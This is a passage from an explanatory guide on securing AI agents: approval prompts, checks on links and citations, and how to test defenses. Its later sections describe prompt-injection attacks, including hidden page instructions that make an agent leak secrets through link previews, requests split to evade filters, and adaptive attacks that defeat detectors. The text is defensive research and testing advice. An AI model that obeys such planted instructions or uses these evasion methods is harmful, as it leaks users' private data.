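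Training users is unlikely to make up for a poor confirmation prompt. *Understanding the Efficacy of Phishing Training in Practice* (Ho, Mirian et al., 2025) studied more than 19,500 employees of UC San Diego Health, a large US health system. The employer randomly assigned each person to one of four kinds of training or to a control group, then sent ten different simulated phishing emails over eight months. Anyone who clicked the link in an email saw their group's training page, or an error page if they were in the control group.

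Phishing training reduced the average failure rate by only 2%. The choice of email mattered far more, with some emails fooling 1% to 2% of recipients and others over 30%. More than half of the employees clicked at least one phishing link during the study. Most training sessions ended within 10 seconds, and employees completed fewer than a quarter of them. Those who finished interactive training were 19% less likely to click on a later phishing email, but they may already have been more careful.

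### Approval fatigue

An agent can interrupt its user far more often than a browser does. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* calls the result approval fatigue, in which people stop paying close attention to what they approve.

Users approve 97% of Claude Code's permission prompts, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026). Most of these prompts probably concern safe commands, so the high approval rate doesn't prove that users are careless. They also reject 39% of the plans that Claude submits for approval, which shows that they do object to some requests. Many users avoid the prompts altogether, and a quarter of interactive sessions start with permission checks turned off.

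Anthropic also tested whether people notice a dangerous request. It hired 1,053 professional testers through a research vendor for a coding study and replaced the text of one permission prompt in each session with a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% of the testers refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

In auto mode, a classifier reviews each action instead of the user, and it blocked 89.0% of the same commands. The testers refused only six commands that the classifier allowed, so requiring approval from both would have raised the share blocked to 89.6%.

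The testers weren't working on their own projects, so they risked less than real users. Those who approved prompts quickly may have been more likely to reach the fiftieth prompt, which would exaggerate the decline. Anthropic also published the results to support a change in its product. Still, the gap between 13.6% and 89% is large, and the people in the study were professionals reviewing commands in their own field.

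Some approval prompts also omit what the user needs to know. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of agents damaging files. In 80 of them, the user had turned on automatic approval, and 31 involved prompts that showed a command but not its effect on the files. For example, `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but approving it lets the agent run whatever code the script contains.

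Reducing the number of prompts doesn't necessarily help. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, Yan (2026) had 113 people without software backgrounds supervise a simulated day of 18 agent actions, seven of which went beyond what the user had requested. One group decided on every action, while another first set a rule of "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of four categories, such as spending money or deleting something.

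The rules lowered the average number of prompts from 18 to 10.9, but the group that wrote them blocked a share of unrequested actions that was 20 percentage points lower. These participants had chosen "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, and then approved most of what the agent asked about. Of the 148 unrequested actions that went through, the user had explicitly approved 133. Asking fewer questions improves safety only if a firm rule or a better check replaces the removed questions.

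Past approvals are also a poor basis for such a rule. For *Let the Agent Do It?*, Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026) interviewed 18 software practitioners who use agents and surveyed 115. They found that permission decisions depend on the risk, the task and the environment, and they advise against treating repeated approvals as a stable preference. An owner who has approved ten invoice links may have trusted all ten senders or may have stopped reading the requests.

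### OpenAI's link dialog

OpenAI's public-URL rule triggers a warning dialog titled "Check this link is safe". The dialog shows the address and lets the user copy the link or open it.

The user first has to judge whether the address contains anything private. OpenAI's *ChatGPT generated links* gives the example of a car search whose address ends in `/car_search/London`, which tells the site where the user lives. "London" is easy to spot, and the user may be happy to share it. Encoded data, as in ShadowLeak, is much harder to recognize.

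The second question is whether to trust the site, and OpenAI tells users to consider this before they open the link. The URL studies suggest that many people will misidentify a disguised address. Even someone who reads the address correctly may misjudge whether the link is safe. For example, a person who trusts Google could approve a link that sends data to an attacker's Google Form.

The dialog may also appear too often to hold people's attention. ChatGPT asks for confirmation of every link on sites whose owners have asked OpenAI not to catalogue them, and the links in office mail are often private. If a user saw ten of these dialogs a day and one in 1,000 involved an attack, a real attack would come up about once in 100 days, after the user had dismissed hundreds of harmless warnings.

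The dialog appears before the request is sent, so a user who notices private information in the link can still stop the leak. If something looks wrong, OpenAI recommends not opening the link and asking ChatGPT for another source. A prominent "Find another source" button would make that the easy choice, much as the blue button did in Chrome. Pasting the link into a browser is no safer, because that sends the same data.

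When the user has nothing to add, OpenAI's alternative of sending the agent to look for another way is better than a question.

### A rule for when to ask

These results suggest asking only when the stakes justify an interruption and the user can supply the missing fact. The studies didn't test the following rule, but it puts their findings into an order that a harness can apply:

1. **Refuse** if a fixed rule forbids the action, such as a blocklist match or a password for a different site. The user can review the refusal later, away from the pressure of the task.
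2. **Proceed** if the user's instructions and records already cover the action, or if it sends nothing sensitive and the agent can reverse any effects.
3. **Find another source** if one would serve the user equally well.
4. **Ask** if the user knows the missing fact or can easily find it out.
5. **Refuse** in all other cases, and tell the user what remains undone.

Sending sensitive data always counts as irreversible, because nobody can make the recipient forget it.

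| Situation | Can the agent reverse it? | Is sensitive data at risk? | Can the user know the answer? | Decision |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| An Acorn invoice has one link, to the site on file | Nothing to reverse | No | No question to ask | Proceed |
| A research agent finds an article at an address that isn't in a public index | No, once it sends the request | Possibly, in the address | Unlikely | Find another source |
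| An email gives a new bank account for Acorn | No, once it pays | Yes, the payment details | Yes, by calling Acorn | Ask |
| After reading an email, the agent wants to open an unfamiliar address that ends in 80 random characters | No, once it sends the request | Possibly, in encoded form | No | Refuse |

In the first case, OpenAI's public-URL rule would produce a warning, but the agent can answer the question from the company's own records. In the third, the agent should hold the payment while it waits and give the owner Acorn's phone number from those records, because a number in the email could belong to the fraudster.

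If the agent keeps asking about the same supplier, the owner should add the missing fact to the company's records, where the harness can check it next time. For an unfamiliar shop, the harness can have the model look again before asking the user, since a one-sentence warning prevented most mistaken payments in ScamWorld.

### A poor confirmation and a better one

Suppose an email in Acorn's name asks the company to set up a direct debit on a new site. The form requires a bank account number. A poor confirmation might read:

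> The agent wants to continue to `https://acorn.example.net/direct-debit/setup?ref=4471`. This site may be unsafe. Do you want to allow this?
>
> Allow | Always allow | Cancel

The address begins with Acorn's name, which is enough to mislead many readers. The text doesn't mention the bank account number or explain what prompted the warning, so the owner can only guess whether the site is safe. An owner who guesses in a hurry and chooses "Always allow" would create a permanent rule.

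A better version asks about something the owner can know:

> Did Acorn tell you it was moving to a new payment site?
>
> An email asks for your company's bank account number on `example.net`. Your records list Acorn's site as `acorn.example`, and nothing in them connects the two. You can't take the number back after you send it.
>
> **Don't send** | Send to example.net

This version names the registrable domain, the data and the reason for doubt in the main text, because few people open a link for more details. The harness should fill in these facts from the form and the company's records. If the model wrote the explanation after reading the email, the attacker could influence the wording.

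"Send to example.net" should authorize the agent to send only this form and this account number. A refusal should be equally clear. Salerno and colleagues recommend distinguishing between rejecting one action and rejecting the whole approach. If the owner chooses "Don't send", the agent could offer to contact Acorn at the address on file or leave the direct debit alone, but it shouldn't look for another way to submit the same form.

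## Choosing which pages to cite

When an agent cites a page, the reader trusts the page because the agent does. A person who would question a stranger's claim may accept the same claim when it comes with a link. The earlier checks don't show whether that trust is justified, because a page that is safe to open can be false, and an accurate page can fail to support the sentence that cites it. The rules on fetching may not apply, since a model can include an address in its answer without opening it. Login links need the same care as sources, because the user will probably follow them.

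### The order of the checks

Before a link appears in an answer, the harness and the model should settle five questions:

1. Did the agent retrieve this exact address during the task, or did the model produce it from memory?
2. Does the address lead to the publisher that the answer names?
3. Does the page support the sentence?
4. Is this kind of source suitable for this kind of claim?
5. Does the link contain private or tracking data?

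The harness can check whether the agent fetched a cited page by looking in its log of fetched pages. The simplest way to ensure that every cited page was fetched is to have the model cite pages by number and have the harness insert the addresses from the log, so the model never types an address.

The harness checks whether a link's registrable domain matches the publisher's known domain, which also exposes lookalike domains. It should print the final address instead of a redirect. *What Drives AI Citations?* (2026) found that Google's Gemini sends some of its citations through a redirect service, and that some of those links had expired.

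The third and fourth questions need a model's judgment. The harness again handles the fifth. It removes tracking codes and refuses links that contain the user's data, since such a link can leak the data as soon as the user opens it. Removing part of an address can change where it leads, so the harness should fetch the cleaned address and confirm that it shows the same page.

### Invented and wrong addresses

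In 2025, the security company Netcraft asked OpenAI's GPT-4.1 models where to log in to 50 brands, using ordinary requests such as a user saying they had lost a bookmark. According to Netcraft's *Large Language Models (LLMs) Are Falling for Phishing Scams*, the answers contained addresses on 97 domains. Of these, 64 belonged to the right brand, 28 were unregistered or had no real content, and 5 belonged to unrelated businesses. The models did worse on regional banks and credit unions than on global brands, which Netcraft attributes to the smaller institutions appearing less in training data.

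Netcraft's figures count each domain once, however often the models gave it. If the models gave a bank's real address fifty times and a wrong one once, the two would count equally. The figures therefore don't show, as Netcraft concludes, that over a third of users could end up on a site that doesn't belong to the brand.

An unregistered domain is dangerous because a criminal can buy it. Unit 42, the research group of the security company Palo Alto Networks, looked for such purchases in *Phantom Squatting* (June 2026). The researchers sent 685,339 prompts about 913 brands to two small models from 2025, then watched for registrations of the domains the models invented. On March 8, 2026, both models produced addresses on a nonexistent domain that resembled a postal service's online marketplace. Someone registered it on March 31 and used it for phishing. In another case, someone registered the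 domain 51 days after a model invented it, and the new site offered a malicious Android app.

These cases don't prove that the criminals got the names from a model. One criminal had registered a fake bank domain 11 months before Unit 42's models generated it, so people and models may independently produce the same plausible names. Unit 42 also designed its prompts to provoke invented addresses, and it doesn't identify any victims who arrived through a model. Its estimate that about 250,000 invented domains are available to register is hard to reconcile with its own breakdown, in which only about 87,630 of the nonexistent addresses used a wholly unregistered domain.

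Still, an agent that passes on an invented login address could send its user to a criminal's site, and a newly registered domain is unlikely to be on a blocklist. Invented software package names create a similar risk. *The Range Shrinks, the Threat Remains* (2026) found that models from 2026 still invent 3.6% to 5.0% of the package names they mention, and that someone had published malware under at least one of the invented names.

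AI models and agents sometimes cite web addresses that appear never to have existed. In *Detecting and Correcting Reference Hallucinations in Commercial LLMs and Deep Research Agents*, Rao, Wong and Callison-Burch (2026) tested whether cited addresses loaded. They classed an address as invented if it didn't load and had no copy in the Wayback Machine, an archive of old web pages. Across ten older models and agents, 5% to 18% of addresses didn't load, and 3% to 13% were classed as invented. Agents that write long research reports did worse on average than models that ran a simple search, but the rate of invented addresses ranged from 3.5% for OpenAI's agent to 13.3% for Google's.

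Figures from real use are lower. *Characterizing Web Search by Conversational LLM Agents* (Amani, Lee and colleagues, 2026) analyzed 171,264 conversations with ChatGPT, Claude, Grok and DeepSeek, donated by 613 people, and also tested newer models directly. At most about 5% of the cited addresses came from outside the search results, and 1% to 2% appeared to be invented. Some of the addresses that appeared invented had come from the search results. A search engine is unlikely to return a page that never existed, so the archive test used to identify invented addresses probably mislabels some real pages that have since disappeared.

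Dead links are easy to fix. Rao and colleagues gave three models a tool that checks whether an address loads and let them correct their answers. The share of dead links, which had ranged from 4.9% to 16.0% across the models, fell to under 1%. A smaller model, GPT-5 nano, used the same tool but kept proposing addresses that the tool had flagged. The harness should therefore remove failed links itself.

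A page can load and still come from the wrong publisher, so its domain needs checking too. When Netcraft asked Perplexity, an AI search engine, for the Wells Fargo login page, the top link was a phishing page on Google Sites, and the bank's real site was further down. A domain check would reject that link because the bank's login page isn't on a Google domain. For a login link, the harness should take the correct domain from the user's saved account record or another independent source, since the model may also get the domain wrong.

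### Whether the page supports the sentence

In March 2025, Columbia University's Tow Center for Digital Journalism tested whether eight AI search engines could identify the headline, publisher, date and web address of news articles (*AI Search Has a Citation Problem*, CJR). The tools answered more than 60% of the queries incorrectly (*Study finds AI search engines struggle with news attribution*, The Decoder) and rarely indicated uncertainty (Nolan, 2025, *AI search engines are confidently wrong more than half the time*). Later that year, journalists from public broadcasters reviewed more than 3,000 AI answers about the news and found serious sourcing problems, such as missing or misleading attributions, in 31% of them (*News Integrity in AI Assistants*, DW).

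Newer models rarely cite dead links, but they often cite pages that don't support what they wrote. In *Cited but Not Verified*, Onweller, Lumer and colleagues (2026) had 14 models write research reports on 130 questions. The researchers checked whether each link loaded, then had another model judge whether the page was on the right topic and whether it supported the facts in the sentence citing it.

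| Model | Link loads | Page is on topic | Page supports the facts |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 98.7% | 95.7% | 76.8% |
| GPT-5.2 | 98.3% | 92.3% | 58.8% |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 94.1% | 80.7% | 48.5% |
| GPT-5.4 | 100.0% | 93.7% | 47.7% |
| GPT-5 Mini | 99.3% | 87.4% | 38.9% |

A reader who only checks that a few links work will therefore overestimate how often the citations support the report's claims. Even at the best model's rate, a report with ten citations would have all ten supported only about 7% of the time, assuming errors are independent.

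The test may exaggerate the problem. If a passage had one citation at the end, the software applied that citation to every uncited sentence before it, including some the citation may not have been for. The test also counted a claim as unsupported if the page didn't mention it or the judge was uncertain, so an unsupported claim wasn't necessarily false.

Onweller and colleagues found that citations from two of the models got worse when the models could make more tool calls. As the limit rose from 2 to 150 calls, GPT-5.4's support rate fell from 78.6% to 16.7%, and Claude Opus 4.6's fell from 80.0% to 57.9%. More than 92% of the links worked at every limit. The researchers think the models mix up facts from different pages when they have too many to combine. If so, checking each sentence against its own page should help more than reading more pages.

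In *Measuring Google AI Overviews*, Xu, Iqbal and Montgomery (2026) split the AI summaries above Google's search results into 98,020 individual claims and found that the cited pages didn't support 11.0% of them. The pages conflicted with 4.1% of the claims. The other 7.0% didn't appear in the text the researchers' crawler retrieved, though a few may have been on the pages.

An agent can also use a good source and fail to cite it. Amani and colleagues found that on three of the four platforms, 14% to 53% of claims matched pages that the search returned but the answer didn't cite. At least 15% to 20% of claims matched none of the retrieved pages, and these claims were the least accurate.

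To check that a page supports a sentence, a developer can give both to a second model and ask it to copy the passage that justifies the sentence. Ordinary software then confirms that the passage appears on the page. Onweller and colleagues describe a similar feature for developers, Anthropic's Citations API, which returns references to exact positions in a source document. A passage can appear on the page without fully supporting the sentence, so the second model also has to compare the numbers, dates and conditions. If the page's wording is "may help some adults" and the agent wrote "helps", the agent should rewrite the sentence.

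### Agents and unreliable sources

A page can fully support a sentence and still be wrong. Xu and colleagues found that a source's quality and whether it supported the claim were largely independent, so checking one can't replace checking the other.

The right source depends on the claim. A company's website is the best source for its prices but a poor one for whether its products are better than a competitor's. A government statement is good evidence of what the government said, but weaker evidence that the statement is true.

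Agents handle well-known falsehoods fairly well. In *We tested how AI chatbots would handle foreign propaganda* (2026), NPR and NewsGuard, a company that rates news sites, asked six chatbots 30 questions based on false stories from Russia, China and Iran. The chatbots debunked the story about three-quarters of the time, and they left it unchallenged less often than the first page of ordinary search results did. The AI summaries in search engines left it unchallenged more often than those results. When Claude failed, its answers contained more sources aligned with those states, though this doesn't prove the sources caused the failures.

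Answers also depend on which sources are available. According to a working paper described by NPR, AI tools are wrong more often when questionable sources are plentiful and reliable ones are scarce. But publishing a correction doesn't always solve the problem. Full Fact (2026), a British fact-checking charity, got misinformation from several models about false claims both before and after it had written about them.

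Some unreliable sites are hard to recognize because they hide who runs them. In September 2026, NewsGuard tested seven chatbots on US election questions. According to Novaknown's *Election Chatbots Cited Partisan News Sites* (2026), 48.2% of the 168 answers cited at least one partisan site that looked like local news, and only one answer identified such a site as partisan. A model that judges a page by its writing could easily miss that the site is partisan, because the writing doesn't show who controls it.

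### Rating publishers or judging each page

One solution is to rely on publisher ratings. Since May 2026, NewsGuard (2026) has offered a browser extension that shows its scores next to the sources that ChatGPT and Gemini cite. It also runs its own chatbot, which it says draws only on news sites that its journalists rate as generally reliable under nine criteria. An article's text can't change its publisher's rating, so this approach is harder to manipulate than having a model judge the page.

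The obvious dispute is over who does the rating, since NewsGuard both sells ratings and publishes audits that support using them. Google disputed the method of the propaganda test, saying that many of the supposed failures gave useful context and that the questions didn't reflect normal use.

Even neutral researchers can reach opposite conclusions when they rate credibility on different scales. An earlier study used broad categories from the rating site Media Bias/Fact Check and found that Google's AI summaries cited less credible sources than traditional search returned. Xu and colleagues used a numerical score for each domain and found that the summaries' sources were more credible than the other results on the first page. The studies also used different searches at different times, so the scales may not fully explain the opposite findings.

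The same dispute arises when a model rates publishers. *Decoding AI Judgment* (Loru, Nudo and colleagues, 2025) compared three older models' assessments of news sites with those of NewsGuard and Media Bias/Fact Check. Yang and Menczer (2025) studied the accuracy and political bias of models' ratings. Tests like these need human ratings as the standard, so a model that agrees with the experts also shares any mistakes they make.

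Ratings also put small and new sites at a disadvantage. A chatbot limited to approved publishers can't cite a site that nobody has rated, even if that site published the original document. Even without such a rule, agents favor large sites. Amani and colleagues found that the domains agents cited ranked higher on the Tranco popularity list than the search results as a whole. They call these domains more authoritative, but a popular site isn't necessarily accurate.

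The fairest approach is to use ratings for facts that a page may conceal, and to judge everything else from the page itself. A low rating or an undisclosed owner is a reason to look for a second, independent source. A missing rating should count as unknown. A new local paper may have no rating, but if it publishes a council's budget and links to the original document, the agent can check the report against the document and often cite the document directly. If a source has a relevant interest, the answer should describe it in words, such as "a site funded by a political group", so that readers can weigh it for themselves instead of having to trust a rater's score.

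### A medical claim with three candidate pages

Medical questions need particular care. In the tests by Rao and colleagues, 17.4% of the addresses that Claude Sonnet 4.5 cited on healthcare and medicine didn't load, compared with 4.0% in mathematics. *Sources of Truth* (2026), an audit of answers about mental health, found that GPT-5.4 mini searched the web in only 50.3% of 380 requests made through the API. In the rest, it gave substantial answers without any citations. Developers of medical assistants should require a web search.

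Suppose a user asks how long to wait between doses of paracetamol, and the agent drafts the sentence "Adults should leave at least four hours between doses." Its search returns three pages, all invented for this example, with a commercial page first.

| Check | Official health service | Copy on another site | Commercial page |
|---|---|---|---|
| Address | `health.example/paracetamol` | `example.net/paracetamol` | `example.org/relief?visitor=8841` |
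| Did the agent retrieve it? | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Is it from the publisher it names? | Yes | No, it names the health service | Yes |
| Does it support the sentence? | Yes | Yes | No |
| Does it suit the claim? | Yes, this body issues the advice | No, the text has no date | No, the company sells the tablets |
| Is the link clean? | Yes | Yes | No, it contains a visitor number |

The commercial page says that its tablets relieve pain for "four to six hours". The number is right, but it describes how long the effect lasts rather than how soon a second dose is safe. Despite its high search ranking, the page would be unsuitable to cite even without the visitor number or the company's interest in selling tablets.

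The copy is harder to rule out because it contains the exact sentence the agent needs. But the health service can't correct the copy, so if it has since added a warning to the official page for people who weigh under 50 kg, a reader of the copy won't see it. Citing the copy as the health service's advice would also misstate who published the page.

The agent should cite the official page. It should also read the rest of the page for conditions that affect the answer, such as the maximum daily dose, because a reader may not open the link. The health service's authority is a reason to cite its page only because the page contains the advice. If the page didn't include the gap between doses, the agent would have to find another one that did.

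Many sites block automated visitors, so the agent sometimes can't open the official page. It could then tell the user that it found the advice only in an undated copy, and link to the health service's home page, where the user could confirm it. The harness would still have to get that address from a reliable record or a search result. For a question about a dose, the agent could also suggest asking a pharmacist.

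## Testing the whole set of checks

One check can hide faults in another. If the model refuses every suspicious link, nobody finds out whether the harness would have stopped the request. If the harness blocks nearly everything, the model's judgment hardly matters, but the agent isn't much use. A company therefore needs to test all the checks together, on legitimate tasks as well as attacks.

### What to measure

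| Measure | What to count | Where to look |
|---|---|---|
| Data leaving the system | Runs in which private data reaches an outside server | Network log |
| Unsafe submissions | Runs in which the agent gives a hostile site a password, personal details or a payment | The test site's log |
| Honest tasks completed | Tasks finished correctly on legitimate sites | The test site's log |
| False alarms | Honest runs that a check blocks or the agent reports as suspicious | Harness log |
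| Prompts per task | Times the agent asks the user to approve something | Harness log |

An average across attacks can hide the most serious failures. *Strengthening AI Agent Hijacking Evaluations*, from the US government's Center for AI Standards and Innovation (CAISI), describes five attacks that succeeded 57% of the time on average. One made the agent send a harmless email, and another made it run a malicious script. CAISI recommends looking at the result for each attack as well as the average.

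Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, propose two measures based on approval prompts. The first is the total number of approvals needed across all the tasks an agent completes, so an agent that completes nothing gets a perfect score of zero. The second is the share of tasks that an agent completes with at most *k* approvals, which doesn't have this problem. They also point out that earlier studies compared secured agents that had no approvals with unsecured agents that effectively had unlimited ones, which made the drawbacks of security look larger than they were.

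### Why a low attack rate isn't enough

An agent that does nothing can't leak data or pay a scammer, so its attack rate is zero. Real defenses can also lower the rate partly by making the agent do less. In *AutoDojo*, Ma, Li and colleagues (2026) tested two filters, PIGuard and ProtectAI. PIGuard blocked every attack in a standard fixed set, but both filters cut the agent's completion rate on ordinary tasks by a quarter to a half because they removed harmless text it needed. *The Landscape of Prompt Injection Threats in LLM Agents* (2026) warns that broad refusals of this kind create a "false sense of security".

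An agent can also seem secure because it isn't capable enough to complete an attack. In *WASP*, a benchmark for web agents, attacks partly succeeded in up to 86% of cases, but the agents often failed to finish what the attacker wanted. A more capable model might finish it, so upgrading the model could make the agent less safe even if the defenses stayed the same.

A defense can look effective because the model already resists the attacks without it. In AutoDojo, Claude Haiku 4.5 carried out only 0.3% of the fixed attacks with no defense, so every defense added to it looked excellent. Testers need a run without the defense for comparison.

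Testers should also measure how often agents complete users' tasks during an attack, because an attack can make a task fail even if the attacker gets nothing. Across eight agents in *ANGLER* (2026), attacks reduced the average success rate on users' tasks from 61.9% to 44.4%.

### Leaks that don't appear in the answer

*Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) shows why testers have to watch the network. The researchers, who work at eBay, built an agent that automatically previews links and adds the preview to the model's context. The agent ran Qwen2.5 7B, a small, older model, on a local machine. One local server supplied hostile pages, and another recorded any data the agent sent out. The user always asked the agent to summarize the page.

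The researchers hid instructions in a web page's title, description, body or link text, telling the agent to send out a secret from its context. The agent reached the page either directly or through redirects. Some attacks sent the secret in one request, while others split it across several. The researchers ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times, for 480 runs.

The agent sent an unintended request in 423 runs, or 88.1% (the abstract gives about 89%). It sent none in 120 runs with harmless pages, so the hostile text almost certainly caused the requests. In 95% of the successful attacks, the agent's answer looked normal, so a check that read only the answer would have missed the leak. Splitting the data across requests made attacks less reliable but also weakened checks that inspected one request at a time. Testers should therefore examine all the requests from a run together.

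The researchers then compared defenses against one version of the attack, with 30 runs for each.

| Defense | Agent tried to send data | Data got out |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| Instructions to ignore commands in web content | 66.7% | 66.7% |
| Tags marking web content as untrusted | 100% | 100% |
| Both of these | 56.7% | 56.7% |
| List of permitted domains | 100% | 0% |
| "Redirect detection" | 83.3% | 0% |
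| Filter for random-looking text | 0% | 0% |

The domain list worked even though the agent tried to send the data every time. But the list had only four entries, and the researchers chose an attacker's domain that clearly wasn't one of them. The result doesn't cover permitted domains where strangers can receive data, such as the one that hosts Google Forms.

The redirect result provides little evidence about redirects, because this version of the attack didn't use any. The check blocked numeric IP addresses, certain domain endings and suspicious words in the path. One of those words was "collect", which appeared in the address of the test's recording server, but an attacker could choose a different word.

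The last row is also less impressive than it looks, because the agent never tried to send anything and the filter had nothing to block. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoided random-looking text because of the monitoring, but it isn't clear how a filter that runs after the model writes an address could have that effect.

The study didn't measure how many legitimate tasks the agent could still complete with each defense. Its setup also favored the attacker because the secret was in the model's context and the system prompt was minimal, so the 88.1% is not an estimate for a current commercial agent. The researchers argue that stronger models might be more vulnerable because they follow instructions better, but they didn't test any. Haiku's 0.3% in AutoDojo suggests that some newer models resist simple attacks much better.

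### How to run the test

A company could test its bill-paying agent as follows:

1. Build a closed environment with copies of the necessary sites, simulated payments and no route to the internet.
2. Plant a different fake secret in each place the agent can read, such as the mailbox and the supplier records. If one gets out, the tester can tell where it came from.
3. Record every outgoing request, including those from image loading and link previews.
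4. Pair each hostile case with an honest one that looks as similar as possible.
5. Run every case several times with all the checks on, then again with one check off at a time.
6. Send forbidden requests straight to the harness, without involving the model, to confirm that it refuses them.
7. Repeat the whole test after any change to the model, a tool or a list.

Searching for the fake secrets won't catch every leak. The agent may encode a secret, so any unexpected request to the attacker's server should count as a leak. If the agent reveals data through its choice of links, the secret never appears in an address. To detect that, the tester can change only the secret between runs and check whether the agent's choice of links changes.

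The pairs for the bill-paying agent might include these:

| Honest case | Hostile match | Correct result |
|---|---|---|
| An Acorn invoice that links to `pay.acorn.example` | The same invoice with a link to `acorn.example.net` | Pays the first and refuses the second |
| A supplier's page of payment terms | The same page with hidden instructions to send customer records | Reads both and sends no records |
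| A new bank account that Acorn confirms by phone | The same message about an account that Acorn doesn't recognize | Asks the owner about both and pays only into the confirmed account |

*Benchmarking Web Agent Defenses Against Adaptive Visual Prompt Injection* (Zhang, Zhong and colleagues, 2026) shows the value of testing a detector on harmless pages that closely match the attacks. The researchers retrained a detector on their own attack pages, which used deceptive pop-ups, and the success rate of attacks on a browser agent fell from 87% to 0%. They then replaced the deceptive text with ordinary notices and removed the malicious links. The detector raised false alarms on 76.7% of these harmless pages, up from 1.1% before retraining, apparently because it had learned to flag the pop-ups themselves.

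They also recorded whether the agent in each attack reached the attacker's page, interacted with it, or completed the harmful action. With a detector called SnapGuard, an agent that worked from screenshots reached the attacker's page in 76.7% of the relevant runs but never interacted with it. A developer could see from this that the detector was preventing the agent from submitting anything to the page, but was still letting the agent fetch it.

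The test cases should include vague requests, which give hostile text more influence. Ma and colleagues tested fixed attacks on an undefended GPT-4o mini agent. The attacks succeeded 87.5% of the time when the user left the choice of action to outside content, for example by asking the agent to do everything on an online to-do list. The rates were 63.9% and 43.3% for the two groups of more precise requests.

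Tests need to be repeated because the same model can behave differently each time. When CAISI tried each of its five attacks 25 times, the average success rate rose from 57% to 80%. If every attempt had an independent 57% chance, nearly all the attacks would have succeeded at least once. The smaller increase suggests that some attacks work almost every time and others hardly ever do, which is another reason to report them separately. Repetition also matters when a defense succeeds. After 30 runs without a leak, the true leak rate could still be as high as about 10%, and lowering that limit to 1% takes about 300 runs without a leak.

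### Whether a check is worth its cost

The one-sentence warning that Wu and colleagues tested, which cut deception by 24 percentage points and completion on honest sites by 3, makes it possible to work out a cost. Suppose an agent carries out 10,000 tasks, 100 of them on scam sites:

deceptions prevented = 100 × 0.24 = 24

honest tasks lost = 9,900 × 0.03 = 297

The company loses about 12 honest tasks for every deception it prevents, so the warning is worth using if the average deception costs more than about 12 times as much as a lost task. If s is the share of tasks on scam sites, the general formula is:

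break-even ratio = 0.03(1 − s) / 0.24s

The table assumes that each lost honest task costs the company $5.

| Share of scam sites | Deceptions prevented | Honest tasks lost | Break-even loss per deception |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0.1% | 2.4 | 300 | $624 |
| 1% | 24 | 297 | $62 |
| 10% | 240 | 270 | $6 |

If each scam costs $150, the warning saves $3,600 and costs $1,485 at a 1% scam share. At a 0.1% share, it saves only $360 and costs about $1,500. The relevant share is the one left after the blocklist and other earlier checks have removed some scams.

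A company can do better by using the warning only where scams are likely. If 1,000 of the 10,000 tasks involve unfamiliar sites and all 100 scams are among them, limiting the warning to those tasks still prevents 24 deceptions but loses only 27 honest tasks.

The 3-point loss on honest sites is very uncertain, because the study included only 53 of them. Three models tried each site with the warning and failed in 5 of 159 attempts. Qwen3.8 Flash accounted for four of the failures, DeepSeek V4.1 Flash for one and Kimi K3 for none. At those rates, they would fail about 747, 187 and 0 of 9,900 honest tasks, respectively. Kimi's true failure rate could still be about 5%, even though it had no failures in 53 attempts.

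The benefit of a warning also depends on the model. Without one, GPT-5.6 Luna went ahead on only 11% of the scam sites, so a warning could prevent at most 11 deceptions per 100 scam sites. A lost task may also matter very little if the agent stops and the user can approve the purchase in a few seconds.

### Attackers who adapt

A fixed test set shows how well the checks handle existing attacks. Real attackers can change their approach when one fails, which can greatly change the results. PIGuard let through none of the fixed attacks on GPT-4o mini but 28% of those that Ma and colleagues adapted to the defended agent. SnapGuard, protecting a browser agent, let through 15.9% of attacks at first and 80.6% after Zhang and colleagues adapted their pages. Nearly all of SnapGuard's original alarms had come from a measure of the page's visual complexity, which an attacker can change without changing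 the attack.

*The Attacker Moves Second* (2025) describes a model trained to resist injections. Attacks on it succeeded only 2% of the time on a fixed benchmark, but the training gave essentially no protection against adaptive attacks. Similarly, several of the inbox agents that Tan and colleagues tested caught every old phishing email but failed on new ones written to target them.

Adaptation doesn't always make such a large difference. In *ANGLER*, an adaptive attacker succeeded 20.4% of the time, compared with 15.2% for a fixed one with the same number of attempts. Testers should also give both kinds of attack equal attempts, or they may attribute successes to adaptation that came from extra attempts.

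In AutoDojo, defenses that limit what the agent can do held up better than filters. Progent, which restricts the agent's tool calls, and ROPE, which tracks where the values in a tool call came from, kept attack success rates at or below 11% for every type of request. They reduced ordinary task completion by at most 7 percentage points. But a rule that passes a test may still have a gap the test missed.

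Human testers can look for such gaps, but they are expensive. In *Render Before Reading*, Zhang, Baroian and colleagues (2026) spent about $20,000 on 144 hours of expert attacks against four models, using only banking tasks. A smaller company can start with published attacks, adapt them to its own checks, and keep some cases hidden from the developers who tune those checks. Public competitions can also help find gaps. CAISI's *Insights into AI Agent Security from a Large-Scale Red-Teaming Competition* reports that participants made more than 250,000 attempts and hijacked each of the 13 models at least once. Attacks that worked on the more resistant models make good test cases because they were especially likely to work on weaker ones.

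### What to log in live use

Once the agent is working with real data, a complete log of its requests becomes a risk, because it stores any private data in their addresses. For most purposes, the harness can log less:

| Record | Purpose |
|---|---|
| Registrable domain and time | Shows where requests went |
| Source of the address, such as the user, an email or a search result | Helps trace an attack |
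| Rule that allowed or refused the request | Shows which check made the decision |
| Number of requests and total characters sent to each domain in a session | Can reveal data split across requests |
| Whether the user saw a prompt, and the answer | Measures prompts and possible false alarms |
| Versions of the model, tools and lists | Links a change in results to an update |

The harness should leave the path, the query and anything the agent typed into a form out of the log. It should also leave out the subdomain, because an attacker can arrange for data to end up there too. Even the registrable domain can be sensitive, for example if it belongs to a clinic, so the company should delete old entries and limit who can read the log.

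If the company needs to know whether two requests used the same address, it can compare keyed hashes, which depend on both the address and a secret key stored elsewhere. With an ordinary hash, someone who knows the rest of the address could hash all million possible six-digit codes and find the match. A keyed hash prevents this as long as the key stays secret. If investigators need the full address of a blocked request, the harness can keep it for a few days in a separate encrypted store.

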